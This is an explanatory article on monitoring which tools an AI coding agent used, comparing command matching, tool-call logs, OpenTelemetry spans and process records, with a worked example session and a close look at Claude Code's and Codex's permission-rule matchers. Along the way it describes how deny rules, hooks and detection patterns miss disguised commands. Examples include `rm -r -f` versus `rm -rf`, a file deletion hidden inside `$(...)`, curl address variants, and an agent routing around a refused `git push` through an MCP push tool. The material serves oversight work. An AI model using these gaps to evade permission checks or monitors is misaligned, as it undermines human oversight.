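# Determining which tools an AI agent used: matching shell commands and reading tool-call logs

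## What a tool call is and where it can be observed

An AI agent is a language model that runs in a loop, requesting an action, receiving the result and choosing what to do next. The model produces only text, and a surrounding program, called the harness, reads that text and acts on it. Claude Code, Codex and Cursor are harnesses for programming work. The harness gives the model a list of tools, each with a name, a description and a set of parameters. Some tools do one narrow thing, such as reading a file. The shell tool, which different harnesses call Bash, Shell, PowerShell or exec_command, passes whatever command the model writes to the machine's shell, the program that interprets typed commands. The shell may then start one program or several hundred.

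A security team may want to know afterwards whether an agent sent data to an outside address, and the maintainers of a benchmark may want to know whether it looked up the answers. Two common ways to find out are command matching and reading the tool-call log. Command matching tests the text of shell commands against patterns to infer which programs ran. The tool-call log is the structured record that the harness writes for each call. The two methods use different evidence and, unless the observer takes care, measure different things.

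### One call, step by step

Suppose a developer asks an agent to get the latest code and run the tests. The harness sends the model the conversation so far and the tool definitions. The model replies with a tool call, which consists of a tool name, some arguments and usually an identifier. Here the name is Bash and the only argument is the command text `git fetch origin && make test`, which has not run yet.

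The harness then checks permission. It may compare the command with rules that the user has set, ask the user directly, run a hook (an outside program that can block the call), or let every call through. If the call is allowed, the harness starts a shell and passes it the command. The shell starts git, which starts ssh if the repository's address requires it. The two ampersands mean that the shell runs make only if git succeeds. Make reads a file in the repository and starts the programs listed there, perhaps Python with a test runner. When the shell exits, the harness collects the output and the exit code, a number that is zero for success and nonzero for failure. It sends both back to the model with the original request's identifier, and the loop repeats.

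A harness's record of this call might look like the following (a constructed example, and real field names differ from one harness to the next):

```json
{
  "session": "s-0417",
  "call_id": "call_7f3a",
  "tool": "Bash",
  "arguments": { "command": "git fetch origin && make test" },
  "requested_at": "10:14:02.110",
  "decision": "allowed_by_user",
  "started_at": "10:14:05.300",
  "ended_at": "10:14:31.900",
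  "exit_code": 2
}
```

The user took three seconds to approve the call, which is the gap between request and start. The record has only one exit code for the whole command line. Make exits with code 2 when it hits an error, so the fetch probably worked and the tests probably failed, but this is a guess based on how make behaves. Ssh, Python and the test runner do not appear in the record.

### Tools from outside the harness

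Some tools come from outside the harness. The Model Context Protocol (MCP), which Anthropic published in November 2024, lets a separate program or remote service, called an MCP server, offer tools. The harness connects to the server, requests its list of tools, and adds their names, descriptions and parameters to the list it gives the model. The model calls these tools in the same form as any other. The harness forwards each call to the server as a `tools/call` message, and the server does the work and returns a result. A local server usually runs as a child process of the harness and exchanges messages with it through the server's own standard input and output, while a remote server communicates over HTTP.

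One shell call can start many programs, whereas a local MCP server starts once and can then handle any number of calls without starting another program. A remote MCP server leaves only a network connection on the local machine, and the harness opens that connection.

### Two meanings of "tool"

"Bash" and "git" are both correct answers to which tool the agent used in the record above. Bash is the harness's tool, and git is a program that Bash started. Counting the values in the log's `tool` field gives answers like "Bash" by default, while matching a pattern against the command text gives answers like "git".

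An agent can open an issue on GitHub by calling an MCP server's issue-creation tool or by running `gh issue create` in the shell, where `gh` is GitHub's command-line program. Filtering the log for the MCP tool's name misses the second route, which is logged as a Bash call, while matching `gh` in shell commands misses the first. Neither search alone can rule out that the agent used GitHub, because the agent can reach GitHub through either a harness tool or a program.

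The two methods can also be combined. The tool-call log normally includes the command text, so an observer can filter the log for shell calls and then match patterns in their arguments. Much command matching works this way, so it misses whatever the log omits.

### Where an observer can stand

The path offers four places to look, and a different party writes the record at each.

The first place to observe a tool call is the network traffic between harness and model. The model's provider handles all of this traffic, as does any gateway, an intermediary server that a company places in between to control cost and access. Wang (2026), in *OpenTelemetry GenAI Conventions*, a post for the gateway vendor TrueFoundry, calls a gateway a strong place to record the model traffic that passes through it, but not a complete trace of an agent, because local tool work and calls that bypass the gateway need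 recording elsewhere. TrueFoundry also offers a harness, so it has some interest in this claim, but the claim follows from the route the traffic takes. The traffic contains what the model requested and the result that the harness later sent back, but not what happened in between, on another machine. Harnesses commonly resend the conversation with each new request, so one tool call can reappear in every later request of the session, and an observer who does not discard repeated identifiers will overcount badly.

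The harness's own log is the natural place to find the permission decision. Its contents depend on what the harness's developers chose to record and what the user's settings exclude, so a reader has to trust both.

The third place is the command text. The model writes it before anything runs, so it is closer to a plan than to a record of events. The observer gets it from the traffic or the log (or, broken up into separate programs, from the operating system), so it is not independent evidence.

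The operating system is the last point on the path where a tool call can be observed. Its kernel handles every program start, and an administrator can have it record each one with its command line and parent process. Linux's audit system and Windows's process-creation events both do this when enabled. Because the kernel doesn't get its information from the model or the harness, these process records are the closest thing to ground truth for checking the other methods. They still miss some actions. Some shell commands, such as `cd` and usually `echo`, run inside the shell and start no program, and neither does a file-reading tool inside the harness. Bash can even open a network connection without starting a program, which only a record of system calls, the requests that programs make to the kernel, would show. An agent with administrator rights might also turn the recording off. Process records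 carry no tool-call identifier, so somebody has to match them to the tool-call log afterwards, usually by parent process or time.

These places differ in which stage of a call they can establish. "The agent used git" might mean that the model requested it, that the harness permitted it, that the program started, or that it finished, and the evidence for each comes from somewhere else:

| Stage | Model traffic | Harness log | Operating system |
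|---|---|---|---|
| Requested | Yes, in the model's reply | Yes | No |
| Permitted | Only by inference from the result | Yes, if the harness logs decisions | No |
| Started | No | The shell, but not the programs under it | Yes, for each program |
| Completed | Yes, if the result went back to the model | Yes, often with an exit code | Yes, if the observer also records exits |

The gaps between stages are common enough to distort a count. If a user refuses a call, a pattern matched against requested commands still counts it as a use. If the fetch in the example above fails, make never starts, although its name is in the text of a permitted, completed call. A program can also keep running after its call completes, as when a command takes a second to start a background server that runs for hours. A call can also complete without succeeding, as the example call did when its tests failed.

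### Matching, logging and counting mistakes

The simplest way to match commands is to search for a word, such as `curl` (a program that transfers data over the network), anywhere in the command. This wrongly reports a use of `curl` for `grep -rn "curl" docs/`, where the agent only searched some documentation for the word. A more careful matcher parses the line by the shell's grammar and checks the command name in each part, so it identifies `grep` as the command and `curl` as an argument. Neither method can find a program whose name is not in the text, such as ssh when git starts it.

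Structured logging records each event as named fields instead of a line of free text. An observer can then filter on `tool` or `exit_code` without guessing where the value appears in a sentence. However, the fields are only as informative as the developer made them, and if the developer left one out, it is missing for every call.

Each method can go wrong in two directions. A false positive is a use that the observer reports but that did not happen, like the `grep` line. A false negative is a use that happened and that the observer did not report. Write $TP$ for the number of correctly reported uses (true positives), and $FP$ and $FN$ for the two kinds of error. Then

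$$\text{precision} = \frac{TP}{TP+FP}, \qquad \text{recall} = \frac{TP}{TP+FN}.$$

Precision is the share of reported uses that were real, and recall is the share of real uses that the observer reported. Accuracy, the share of all judgments that were right, is not much help here because it requires a count of the programs that the observer correctly did not report, and there is no natural way to count programs an agent did not run. Precision is easier to measure than recall because an analyst can sample the reported uses and check each one. Measuring recall requires finding the uses that the observer missed, which takes a second, more complete record.

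Precision and recall are meaningful only once the observer has chosen the unit to count: tool calls, program starts, or whole sessions. Suppose a session has two relevant shell calls: a plain `curl` command, which starts curl once, and `./deploy.sh`, a script that starts curl fifty times. A matcher that looks for `curl` in command text reports the first call and misses the second. Its recall is 1 by session, because it found the only session that used curl. Recall is 0.5 by call, because it found one of two, and about 0.02 by program start, because it found one of 51. Precision is 1 in every case. All three recall figures are correct, so a comparison of two methods that used different units would be worthless.

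### The OpenTelemetry conventions

Harnesses largely use their own log formats. The main attempt at a common format is from OpenTelemetry, an open-source project that standardises how software records its own operation. Its basic unit is the span, a record of one operation with a start and an end, and spans nest inside one another to form a trace. OpenTelemetry's *Inside the LLM Call* shows a trace from VS Code Copilot, Microsoft's coding assistant, with an `invoke_agent` span at the top, a `chat` span below it for each call to the model, and an `execute_tool` span for each tool invocation.

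The execute-tool span is the one that bears on tool use. OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans* defines its fields in an edition from before the project tightened the rule on tool names:

| Field | Requirement level | Content |
|---|---|---|
| `gen_ai.operation.name` | Required | Should be `execute_tool` |
| `gen_ai.tool.name` | Recommended | The harness's name for the tool |
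| `error.type` | Required if the operation ended in an error | A class of error, such as `timeout` |
| `gen_ai.tool.call.id` | Recommended if available | The call's identifier |
| `gen_ai.tool.description` | Recommended if available | What the tool does |
| `gen_ai.tool.type` | Recommended if available | `function`, `extension` or `datastore` |
| `gen_ai.tool.call.arguments` | Opt-in | The parameters, including any command text |
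| `gen_ai.tool.call.result` | Opt-in | What the tool returned, if it succeeded |

OpenTelemetry's conventions used to recommend, but not require, that a record of tool use include the tool's name. OpenTelemetry has since made the field Required and labelled the change as breaking, meaning that existing software may have to adapt. The database vendor Greptime (2026) places the new rule in version 1.41 of the conventions.

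The opt-in rows matter most for the choice between matching and logging. Command text is an argument of the shell tool, and arguments can contain passwords or personal data, so OpenTelemetry attaches a warning to that field and leaves it out by default. Copilot's default telemetry, as OpenTelemetry describes it, includes model names, token counts and durations but not prompt content or tool arguments, which a separate setting turns on. Under such defaults, an observer can see that the agent called the shell tool forty times but can't tell whether any of those calls ran git, because there is no command text to match. Turning capture on may not fully solve this, because the conventions also let software shorten long message contents, and a long command could lose its end.

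The table has no field for a permission decision or an exit code. A refused call never runs, so it may well leave no execute-tool span. The request would then appear only in the recorded chat messages, which are also opt-in. A failed test run is ambiguous too, because the convention does not specify whether a shell tool that ran normally and returned a non-zero code "ended in an error". Two harnesses could therefore both follow the convention and record the same failed run differently.

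The call identifier joins a request to its result. OpenTelemetry's *Gen AI*, the project's list of field definitions, includes an example in which the model calls a weather function and the result comes back under the same identifier. (The second copy in that example has a stray space at the front, so an exact comparison would fail to pair them. Real logs have blemishes of this sort, and code that joins records has to allow for them.)

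OpenTelemetry has separate conventions for MCP, which were added in version 1.39 according to Greptime. They define one span on the harness's side of a call and another on the server's, connected by a shared trace context. OpenTelemetry also allows MCP instrumentation and general instrumentation to trace the same tool execution, so a single MCP call can in principle produce several spans, and counting all of them would overstate the number of calls.

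An absent span is weak evidence that no call took place. Software has to create each span, and OpenTelemetry encourages developers to add spans by hand for tool calls that automatic instrumentation does not cover. Codex and Claude Code both export OpenTelemetry data. In May 2026, OpenTelemetry listed log events and metrics for both, but traces only for Claude Code, in beta. Wang points out that a system can send valid OpenTelemetry data and still use its own names and meanings for the fields.

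OpenTelemetry also still labels the conventions "Development", which means they may change. In June 2026 the project moved the generative-AI conventions from its main collection to their own repository and replaced the old text with a page titled *Moved*. Wang found that the new repository still carried the Development label and had no official release as of 21 August 2026, and advises teams to pin the version they emit and test against it. Version 1.37 replaced the field `gen_ai.system` with `gen_ai.provider.name`, but OpenTelemetry tells libraries on version 1.36 or earlier to keep emitting the old format by default and to switch only when the user sets an environment variable. A search for the new field name will therefore miss model calls recorded by these libraries unless the user has set that variable.

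## One session of eight tool calls, scored by five observers

The following session is made up, so we know the true answer in advance. An agent makes eight tool calls while preparing a software release, and the question is which of them caused git to run on the agent's machine. Git is the program most developers use to track versions of their code.

| Call | Harness tool | Request | What happened on the machine | Did git run? |
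|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Bash | `git status` | Git started once | Yes |
| 2 | Bash | `cd app && git log -5` | The shell changed directory, then git started once | Yes |
| 3 | Bash | `grep -rn "git push" docs/` | Grep searched the documentation | No |
| 4 | Bash | `make release` | Make started git once, to read the latest version tag | Yes |
| 5 | Bash | `python build.py` | Python started git once, to read the current commit | Yes |
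| 6 | MCP | `create_pull_request` | The harness sent a request to GitHub's remote server | No |
| 7 | Bash | `git push` | Nothing, because the harness refused the call | No |
| 8 | Read | `README.md` | The harness opened the file itself | No |

The true answer is calls 1, 2, 4 and 5. Each starts git exactly once, so counting calls and counting program starts give the same total. (Real git is less tidy. A single `git fetch` often starts further copies of git to do parts of its work.)

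Five observers try to answer the question. Two look only at the text of the requested commands. One of these uses an anchored pattern, which matches only if the command starts with `git`, and the other searches for `git` anywhere in the command. A third observer parses each command by the shell's grammar and uses the outcome field in the tool-call log to discard calls that never ran. A fourth reads only the tool names in the log, and a fifth reads the operating system's process records.

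| Observer | Reports | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|
| Anchored pattern | 1, 7 | 1/(1+1) = 1/2 | 1/(1+3) = 1/4 |
| Search for `git` anywhere | 1, 2, 3, 7 | 2/(2+2) = 1/2 | 2/(2+2) = 1/2 |
| Shell parser with outcome field | 1, 2 | 2/(2+0) = 1 | 2/(2+2) = 1/2 |
| Tool names alone | No answer | – | – |
| Process records, every git start | 1, 2, 4, 5 and two runs by the harness | 4/(4+2) = 2/3 | 4/(4+0) = 1 |
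| Process records, using parentage | 1, 2, 4, 5 | 4/(4+0) = 1 | 4/(4+0) = 1 |

These fractions depend on the mix of calls in the example, but the causes of the errors apply more generally.

### Text that only mentions a program

The search for `git` anywhere gets call 2 right but wrongly counts call 3, a documentation search like the earlier `curl` example, as a use of git. The anchored pattern gets call 3 right because the command starts with `grep`, but it misses the use of git in call 2 because that command starts with `cd`.

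The search does worse if the observer runs it over whole log records instead of just the command text. Claude Code names MCP tools by server and tool, according to Anthropic's *Hooks reference*, so call 6 might appear as `mcp__github__create_pull_request`. That name contains "git", so the search matches calls 1, 2, 3, 6 and 7, and its precision drops to 2/5.

A shell parser gets both call 2 and call 3 right.

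Anthropic also documents a working example that uses a plain text search, a hook that blocks destructive deletions. A filter first checks whether any part of the command runs `rm`, the program that deletes files, and then a script searches the whole command for the text `rm -rf`. If an agent runs `rm notes.txt && grep -rn "rm -rf" docs/`, the first half passes the filter, the second half contains the text, and the hook blocks a harmless command. If the agent instead runs `rm -r -f build`, which does the same as `rm -rf build`, the script finds no match and the hook doesn't block the command.

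The filter in that example is also designed to err towards false positives. When Claude Code can't work out which commands a line will run, it runs the hook anyway. A filter for `git push *` therefore fires on `echo $(date)`, which doesn't involve git. This is sensible for a safety check, since a needless check does little harm, but someone who reused the hook to count pushes would overcount them. Anthropic calls the filter best-effort and recommends its permission system for hard limits.

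### Calls that never ran

Call 7 is a real git command that the harness blocked. A better parser can't exclude it, because the command text is the same whether or not the call ran. With the parser alone, the observer would report calls 1, 2 and 7, for a precision of 2/3. Checking the outcome field removes call 7 and raises precision to 1.

How easily an observer can exclude refused calls depends on how the harness records them. Anthropic's *Monitoring usage*, the guide to Claude Code's exported telemetry, describes one event for the permission decision and another for the result. A refused call produces a decision marked "reject" and no result event. Both events carry the call's identifier, so an observer can join them and keep only the calls that have results. The events include the command text only if the setting for tool details is on.

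Other harnesses report refusals and failures in much the same way. *An Empirical Study of Harness Design for Coding Agents (2026)* includes the shell tool description that one harness gives the model. By default, this harness refuses `git push` with a "denied" error but lets `git status` and `git log` run without asking. It also marks any command with a nonzero exit code as an error. An error could therefore mean the harness refused the command, or the command ran and failed.

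Suppose `app` in call 2 isn't part of a git repository. Git runs but exits with an error because it finds no repository, so the true answer is the same. An observer who discards every error now drops call 2 along with call 7, and recall falls from 1/2 to 1/4. An observer who keeps every error counts call 7 again. The observer needs to read the error message, or some other field that distinguishes the two cases.

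If `app` doesn't exist, `cd` fails and git never starts, but the parser still counts git. The exit code may hint at which command failed, since `cd` and git usually fail with different codes, but the observer has to know which codes each program uses.

What an observer records also depends on when it collects the data. In Claude Code, a hook that runs before a tool call receives call 7 because it fires before the normal permission check. The `PostToolUse` hook fires only after a call succeeds, and failures go to a separate hook, so a logging script attached only to `PostToolUse` would miss every git command that ran and failed.

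### Programs started by other programs

Calls 4 and 5 defeat every method that relies on command text, since neither `make release` nor `python build.py` contains the word "git". Write $d$ for the number of calls that name git and run it, and $i$ for the number that run it only through some other program. Then a perfect parser with perfect outcome data has

$$\text{recall} = \frac{d}{d+i},$$

which is 2/4 here. Improving the parser can't raise this number. It depends on how much of the agent's work goes through build files and scripts.

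An observer with a copy of the repository could search the makefile for git. This sometimes works, but agents edit files as they go, so the copy may differ from the version that ran. Make also runs only the parts of the file that the requested target needs, so a line that mentions git may not have run. For `build.py`, the observer would have to trace the logic of the program and any libraries it loads.

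Reading the log by tool name fails for a related reason. The log lists six Bash calls, one MCP call and one Read call, and anything that might be git is recorded only as Bash. Calls in real sessions are often just as concentrated in a few tools. In *TraceLab (2026)*, a study of coding-agent traces, the three most common tools account for over 80% of Claude's calls and 95% of Codex's.

An observer with only these names could guess that every Bash call ran git. This guess has a precision of 4/6 and a recall of 1, the same as the unfiltered process records, so scores from eight calls are weak evidence. In a session with 600 shell calls and the same four git runs, the guess's precision would fall to 4/600, while that of the process records would stay at 4/6 if the harness still ran git only twice.

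Process records do include the git runs in calls 4 and 5. For this session they might give the following tree, in which an analyst has added the call numbers:

```text
harness
├─ git rev-parse HEAD               (harness, at session start)
├─ git status --porcelain           (harness, at session start)
├─ bash                             (call 1)
│  └─ git status
├─ bash                             (call 2)
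│  └─ git log -5
├─ bash                             (call 3)
│  └─ grep -rn "git push" docs/
├─ bash                             (call 4)
│  └─ make release
│     └─ git describe --tags
└─ bash                             (call 5)
   └─ python build.py
      └─ git rev-parse HEAD
```

Git appears six times. The harness ran it the first two times, to collect information about the repository before the model had requested anything. For example, *atomcode-core 4.23.1*, an open-source coding agent, captures the git branch, current commit and state of the working files once at the start of a session so that it can include them in the model's instructions. The harness's two runs did happen on the machine, and they are false positives only because the question was about the agent's tool calls.

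The command line alone can't separate the harness's own git runs from the agent's. The harness and `build.py` both ran `git rev-parse HEAD`, and the two records differ only in the parent process. Tracing the parent processes upwards shows a shell between git and the harness in call 5, but none in the harness's own run. Removing the git runs without a shell above them leaves the correct four. Tracing parents also rules out any git commands that the developer typed in another window, since those don't lead back to the harness.

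When Bash receives a single command to run, it often replaces itself with that command instead of starting a child process. In call 1, git could then take over the shell's process number and have the harness as its direct parent. A rule that discards every git run directly under the harness would then wrongly remove call 1, so the observer has to check whether the same process number first belonged to a shell.

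Filtering by parent process can also fail when work happens later or elsewhere on the machine. *AgentLoupe* (Bao, Liu and colleagues, 2026) reports that existing methods of attributing system actions to an agent fail for delayed execution and for behaviour that crosses process lineages. Suppose `make release` had only written a job file, and a build service that was already running had picked it up ten minutes later and started git. The service would be git's parent, so the filter would discard a run that the agent had caused. AgentLoupe follows such cases by attaching a label to each interaction with the model and carrying it through processes, files and network sockets. The build service would pick up the label when it read the job file.

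### Actions on another machine

Call 6 opened a pull request, which is a proposal to merge one branch of code into another. The tool-call log records the tool's name, arguments and outcome. If the question is instead whether the agent called the pull-request tool, even the observer who reads only tool names gets a precision and recall of 1, as long as the log keeps the full name.

The command patterns have nothing to match, because call 6 has no command text. Process records don't show the call either, because the harness started no program. Both have a recall of 0/1. Their precision is undefined, because neither detects anything and the formula would divide zero by zero.

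GitHub's server usually works this way. GitHub (2026) hosts the remote version and lists `create_pull_request` among its tools, with the owner, repository, title and two branches as required arguments. A developer can also run the server locally, for example in a Docker container, in which case the process records would show only that the tool was available.

A log's settings can still hide which tool the agent used. For MCP servers that the user has configured, Anthropic replaces the tool's name with `mcp_tool` in the permission-decision event, and includes the real server and tool names only when detail logging is on. Otherwise, the event shows only that the agent requested an MCP tool. A badly written filter can also report no calls when there were some. In Claude Code's hooks, `mcp__github` matches no tool because the harness treats it as a complete name. The pattern `mcp__github__.*`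 matches every tool on that server.

Whether the agent opened a pull request is a slightly different question, because an agent can also do that with a shell command. Claude Code has a counter that goes up either way, so it suits this question better than a search for one tool's name. GitHub's own list of pull requests is a check that doesn't depend on the harness, although it doesn't establish which tool opened a pull request.

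The same split between machines limits what an observer can conclude from the refused `git push`. GitHub's server also offers a tool called `push_files`, which takes file contents as arguments and puts them in a repository. After the refusal, an agent could have used it to send its changes to GitHub without running git locally. The process records would correctly show no `git push`, even though the code had left the machine.

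## Claude Code's permission rules: a command matcher and its documented limits

Before Claude Code runs a shell command, it compares the command's text with permission rules written by the user or an administrator. An allow rule lets a matching command run without a prompt, an ask rule makes Claude Code ask the user first, and a deny rule blocks the command. To enforce a deny rule on `git push`, Claude Code has to recognise a `git push`, and a monitor that counts tool use has to do the same. Anthropic documents the matching in enough detail to follow it step by step, including several cases where it fails.

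As of June 2026, 49.5% of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had created an allow rule for Bash by hand, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026).

### What a wrong match costs

Whether a wrong match (a false positive) or a missed match (a false negative) is worse depends on what the match is for:

| Purpose of the match | Wrong match | Missed match |
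|---|---|---|
| Allow rule | A command runs without review | The user gets a needless prompt |
| Deny rule | Claude Code blocks a harmless command | The command goes on to the other rules and the permission mode |
| Monitor | An overcount, or a false accusation | An undercount, or an incident that nobody notices |

When it's unclear whether to allow a command, Claude Code's permission check can show it to the user and wait for an answer. Someone monitoring tool use from the log a week later can't ask, and has to record a use, record no use, or mark the case as unclear. But mistakes in monitoring are easier to repair. An analyst can correct a pattern and run it again, whereas a wrong allow rule may already have let a command delete something.

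Needless prompts can also do harm. Anthropic reports that users approve 97% of Claude Code's permission prompts, and most of those commands are probably safe. In an experiment with 1,053 paid testers, the company replaced one prompt in each coding session with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Anthropic published these figures to justify replacing most prompts with an automatic classifier, and the testers had less to lose than real users because they weren't working on their own code. Still, the fall within a session suggests that prompting too often makes each prompt less useful.

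### From command text to a match

A rule is a tool name, optionally followed by a pattern in parentheses. The simplest pattern is exact text. In an example from Anthropic's *Configure permissions*, `Bash(npm run build)` matches only that command. An asterisk stands for any text, including spaces, so `Bash(git log *)` covers every `git log` command and `Bash(git *)` covers every git command.

A space before a final asterisk changes what a rule matches. `Bash(ls *)` matches `ls` and `ls -la` but not `lsof`, an unrelated program that lists open files, while `Bash(ls*)` matches all three. An observer who wants to reuse these rules on a log could write them roughly as the regular expressions `^ls( .*)?$` and `^ls.*$`, where `^` and `$` mark the start and end of the text. The first form doesn't work for every rule, because a final asterisk matches the bare command only if it is the rule's only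 asterisk. For example, `Bash(* --help *)` matches `npm --help x` but not `npm --help`. Any asterisk in a rule acts as a wildcard, so a user can't write a rule that matches only `find . -name '*.tmp' -delete`.

An asterisk in the middle of a pattern can match more than its author meant. `Bash(git * main)` matches `git merge main`, but it also matches `git push origin main`. Claude Code warns at startup about allow rules that have an asterisk before the subcommand (here, `merge` or `push`).

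Claude Code doesn't apply these patterns to the raw line. It first splits the line at the shell's separators, which are `&&`, `||`, `;`, `|`, `|&`, `&` and line breaks. Call the resulting parts $c_1, \dots, c_n$. If $A(c)$ means that the rules or the built-in list of read-only commands allow part $c$, and $D(c)$ means that a deny rule matches it, then

$$\text{allowed} = A(c_1) \land \dots \land A(c_n), \qquad \text{denied} = D(c_1) \lor \dots \lor D(c_n).$$

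Every part of a command line must be allowed for the line to run without a prompt, but a single denied part blocks the whole line. Denial takes priority when both apply. A monitor needs to check whether any part matches, as the deny rule does, because an agent used git if any part of the line ran git. On the eight-call session above, `Bash(git *)` would match calls 1, 2 and 7, the same calls that the shell parser reported before it used the outcome field.

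Commands can also contain other commands. The shell runs whatever is inside `$(...)` and replaces it with the output, so `echo "$(git clean -f)"` deletes untracked files even though the line starts with `echo`. Claude Code applies deny and ask rules to these nested commands, and to commands inside subshells and loop bodies.

Wrappers are small commands that exist only to run another command under some condition. For example, `timeout 30 npm test` runs the tests and stops them after 30 seconds. Claude Code removes `timeout`, `time`, `nice`, `nohup`, `stdbuf` and a few shell keywords before matching, so a rule for `npm test` still applies. It does not remove `command -v`, which only looks up a program. A monitor should copy that exception, because agents may well use `command -v git` to check whether git is installed, and counting that as a use of git would be a false positive.

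The wrapper list is fixed and leaves out programs such as `npx` and `docker exec` that also run whatever command follows them. A monitor that used the same list would record `npx eslint src` as a use of npx, not eslint. Users can write a rule that names both the runner and the inner command, but they need a separate rule for each inner command.

A command may also start by setting a variable, as in `NODE_ENV=test npm test`. Deny and ask rules ignore any such assignment and match what follows. Allow rules ignore only assignments to variables that Anthropic considers safe. The caution makes sense because some variables change what the command does. For instance, the shell looks for programs in the directories listed in `PATH`, so setting it can change which file runs as `git`.

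In PowerShell, one command can have several names. Claude Code converts common aliases before matching, so a rule for `Get-ChildItem` also covers `gci`, `ls` and `dir`. Someone searching raw logs would need to account for these aliases too.

### When the matcher cannot tell

Claude Code can't parse some commands. In `npm test &&`, nothing follows the ampersands, so Claude Code treats the line as unparseable and doesn't split it. It also doesn't approve the line under `Bash(npm *)`, even though the text matches that rule. In Manual mode, where the user reviews actions that the rules don't settle, a command longer than 10,000 characters always causes a prompt because it is too long to parse. Agents can reach that length by writing a whole script or data file into one command.

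Allow and deny rules treat doubt differently, and the cost table explains why. An allow rule's worst error is a wrong match, so it should match only when the evidence is complete. A deny rule's worst error is a missed match, so it should match on partial evidence. Anthropic applies this beyond shell commands:

| Doubtful case | Allow rule | Deny rule |
|---|---|---|
| Several commands on one line | The rules must cover every part | One matching part is enough |
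| The line first sets a variable not on the safe list | No match | Match |
| A file path is a link to another file | The path and its target must both match | Either one is enough |
| The rule has a wildcard in the tool name | Valid only after the name of a specific MCP server | Valid anywhere in the name |

The asymmetry has a limit, because a deny rule has no effect on a command whose form it doesn't match at all. The result then depends on the other rules and the permission mode. In Manual mode the user may still get a prompt, but in the mode that bypasses permissions the command runs.

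A monitor could use both readings. The strict one counts the uses the text clearly supports, and the loose one adds lines that might contain a use. If the strict reading finds 40 uses of curl and the loose reading finds 46, the six doubtful lines are few enough to check by hand. The true number could still be higher than 46, because neither reading can find programs that a script starts. Lines that can't be parsed should have their own count, because recording them as "no match" would imply that the agent didn't use the tool, when the parser just couldn't read the line.

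### Why patterns on arguments are fragile

Recognising curl is easier than recognising what the agent did with it. Anthropic gives the example of `Bash(curl http://github.com/ *)`, a rule meant to limit curl to addresses on GitHub. The documentation lists four variations that the rule misses:

- an option before the address, as in `curl -X GET http://github.com/...`
- a different protocol, `https` instead of `http`
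- a short address on another site that redirects to GitHub
- a variable that holds the address, as in `URL=http://github.com && curl $URL`

A better pattern could handle the first two, since the information is in the text. For the variable, the observer has to work out its value, which is easy here but impossible from the text if the value comes from a file. The redirect is harder, because the address in the command belongs to another site, whose server determines the final destination when the request arrives. No pattern on the command can recover that destination, although a record of network connections might.

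The example seems to be even narrower than Anthropic's list implies. Under the documentation's rule about a space before a final asterisk, the pattern needs a space or the end of the command right after `github.com/`. It would miss `curl http://github.com/` followed directly by a repository name, which is probably what its author most wanted to allow. The asterisk also accepts any later text, and curl accepts more than one address, so a match doesn't prove that curl contacted only GitHub.

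When an allow rule misses these four commands, Claude Code prompts the user four times. A count of GitHub downloads that used the same matching would have four false negatives, all on commands that an agent might write without trying to hide anything.

The hook filter described earlier runs the hook whenever a command contains a substitution or a variable, which avoids guessing at arguments. Anthropic limits this to filters that specify more than the program's name, so a hook filtered with `Bash(rm *)` still doesn't run on `echo $(date)`.

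For web addresses, Anthropic suggests denying curl and similar programs and having the agent use WebFetch, a harness tool that fetches pages. A rule such as `WebFetch(domain:example.com)` checks the host name in the requested address, so options and protocols no longer affect the match. Anthropic adds that this alone doesn't prevent network access, because an agent that can still run shell commands may use them to reach the network.

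### Tool names and input parameters

Matching can be exact outside the command text because there is no shell grammar to interpret. A rule on a tool name compares two short strings. Deny and ask rules can also test a single input parameter. For example, `Agent(model:opus)` matches a request to start a subagent (a second agent that works for the first) when the `model` field is `opus`.

Claude Code compares a rule with the literal value that the model sent, so `Agent(model:opus)` doesn't match a call that specifies Opus by its full identifier. `Agent(model:*)` matches any value, but it doesn't match a call that omits the field and gets the default. An observer counting subagents by model would therefore need a table of equivalent names and a way to find the default.

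Tool names have similar problems. The transcript may show a tool as "Stop Task", but rules match only its real name, `TaskStop`. Shell commands also don't always go through the Bash tool. In Cowork, part of Anthropic's desktop app, the agent runs them through `mcp__workspace__bash`, and Claude Code's Monitor tool can start them as well. Since version 2.1.314, a `Bash` hook that runs before a call also covers Monitor's shell commands, but a `Bash` hook that runs after a successful call doesn't. A script that logs completed Bash calls would miss those commands, and its output wouldn't show that they were missing.

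Claude Code does not apply parameter matching to the shell tool's `command` field. It ignores a rule such as `Bash(command:rm *)` and warns at startup. A parameter rule compares the whole value, so this one would miss the `rm` in `cd dir && rm file`. The ordinary form `Bash(rm *)` works better because Claude Code splits the line into separate commands before matching.

The exclusion also matters for anyone reading a structured log. The `command` field looks like any other named field, but its value is a small shell program, so searching it is still command matching.

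### Commands that a pattern does not anticipate

A Bash rule matches the text Claude writes, after Claude Code splits the line and removes wrappers. Anthropic explains that the rule covers the form Claude usually produces and "isn't a security boundary around the program". Commands that look different can run the same program, and whoever writes a rule can't foresee all of them. For limits that don't depend on the text, Anthropic points users to its sandbox, where the operating system restricts the files and network addresses a command can reach.

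A rule that matches the usual form of a command may be good enough for a count. If an agent nearly always types `git push` in the ordinary way, the rule will find nearly all of its direct pushes, and an analyst can estimate the rest by checking a sample against process records. That estimate holds only while the agent has no reason to avoid the pattern. After a refusal, an agent may try another form of the command to finish its task, so the rule is least reliable for commands that follow a refusal.

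Security teams run similar patterns over the command lines of whole companies. In *You Cannot Escape Me*, Uetz, Herzog and colleagues (2023) tested a public set of such rules for Windows and report that they could fully or partly evade 129 of the 292 rules (44%) by rewriting the command line. The 44% is the share of rules that someone could evade on purpose, so it doesn't estimate how many ordinary commands a matcher misses. The rules worked on process records, so better evidence about what ran doesn't by itself fix a weak pattern.

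An observer who correctly identifies the program may still learn very little about what the command does. Many users have allow rules for interpreters such as Python and Node, which run code in a general-purpose language. Anthropic puts the share at 43%, but doesn't make clear whether that means all active users or only those with a rule. It considers these rules essentially equivalent to allowing any shell command, and Claude Code sets them aside in auto mode, where a classifier reviews actions. Similarly, a monitor that sees `python build.py`, as in call 5 of the eight-call session, can't tell from the command alone what the script does.

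### How Codex matches commands

Codex solves the same problem with a stricter parser. OpenAI's *Rules*, the guide to a feature the company still calls experimental, explains how to control which commands may run outside Codex's sandbox. A rule's pattern is a list of words, such as `["gh", "pr", "view"]`, and it matches any command that starts with those words. A pattern for `ls` therefore doesn't match `lsof`, which is a different word. The words must appear in order with nothing between them, so the `gh` pattern misses `gh pr --repo openai/codex view 7888`, which has an option before `view`.

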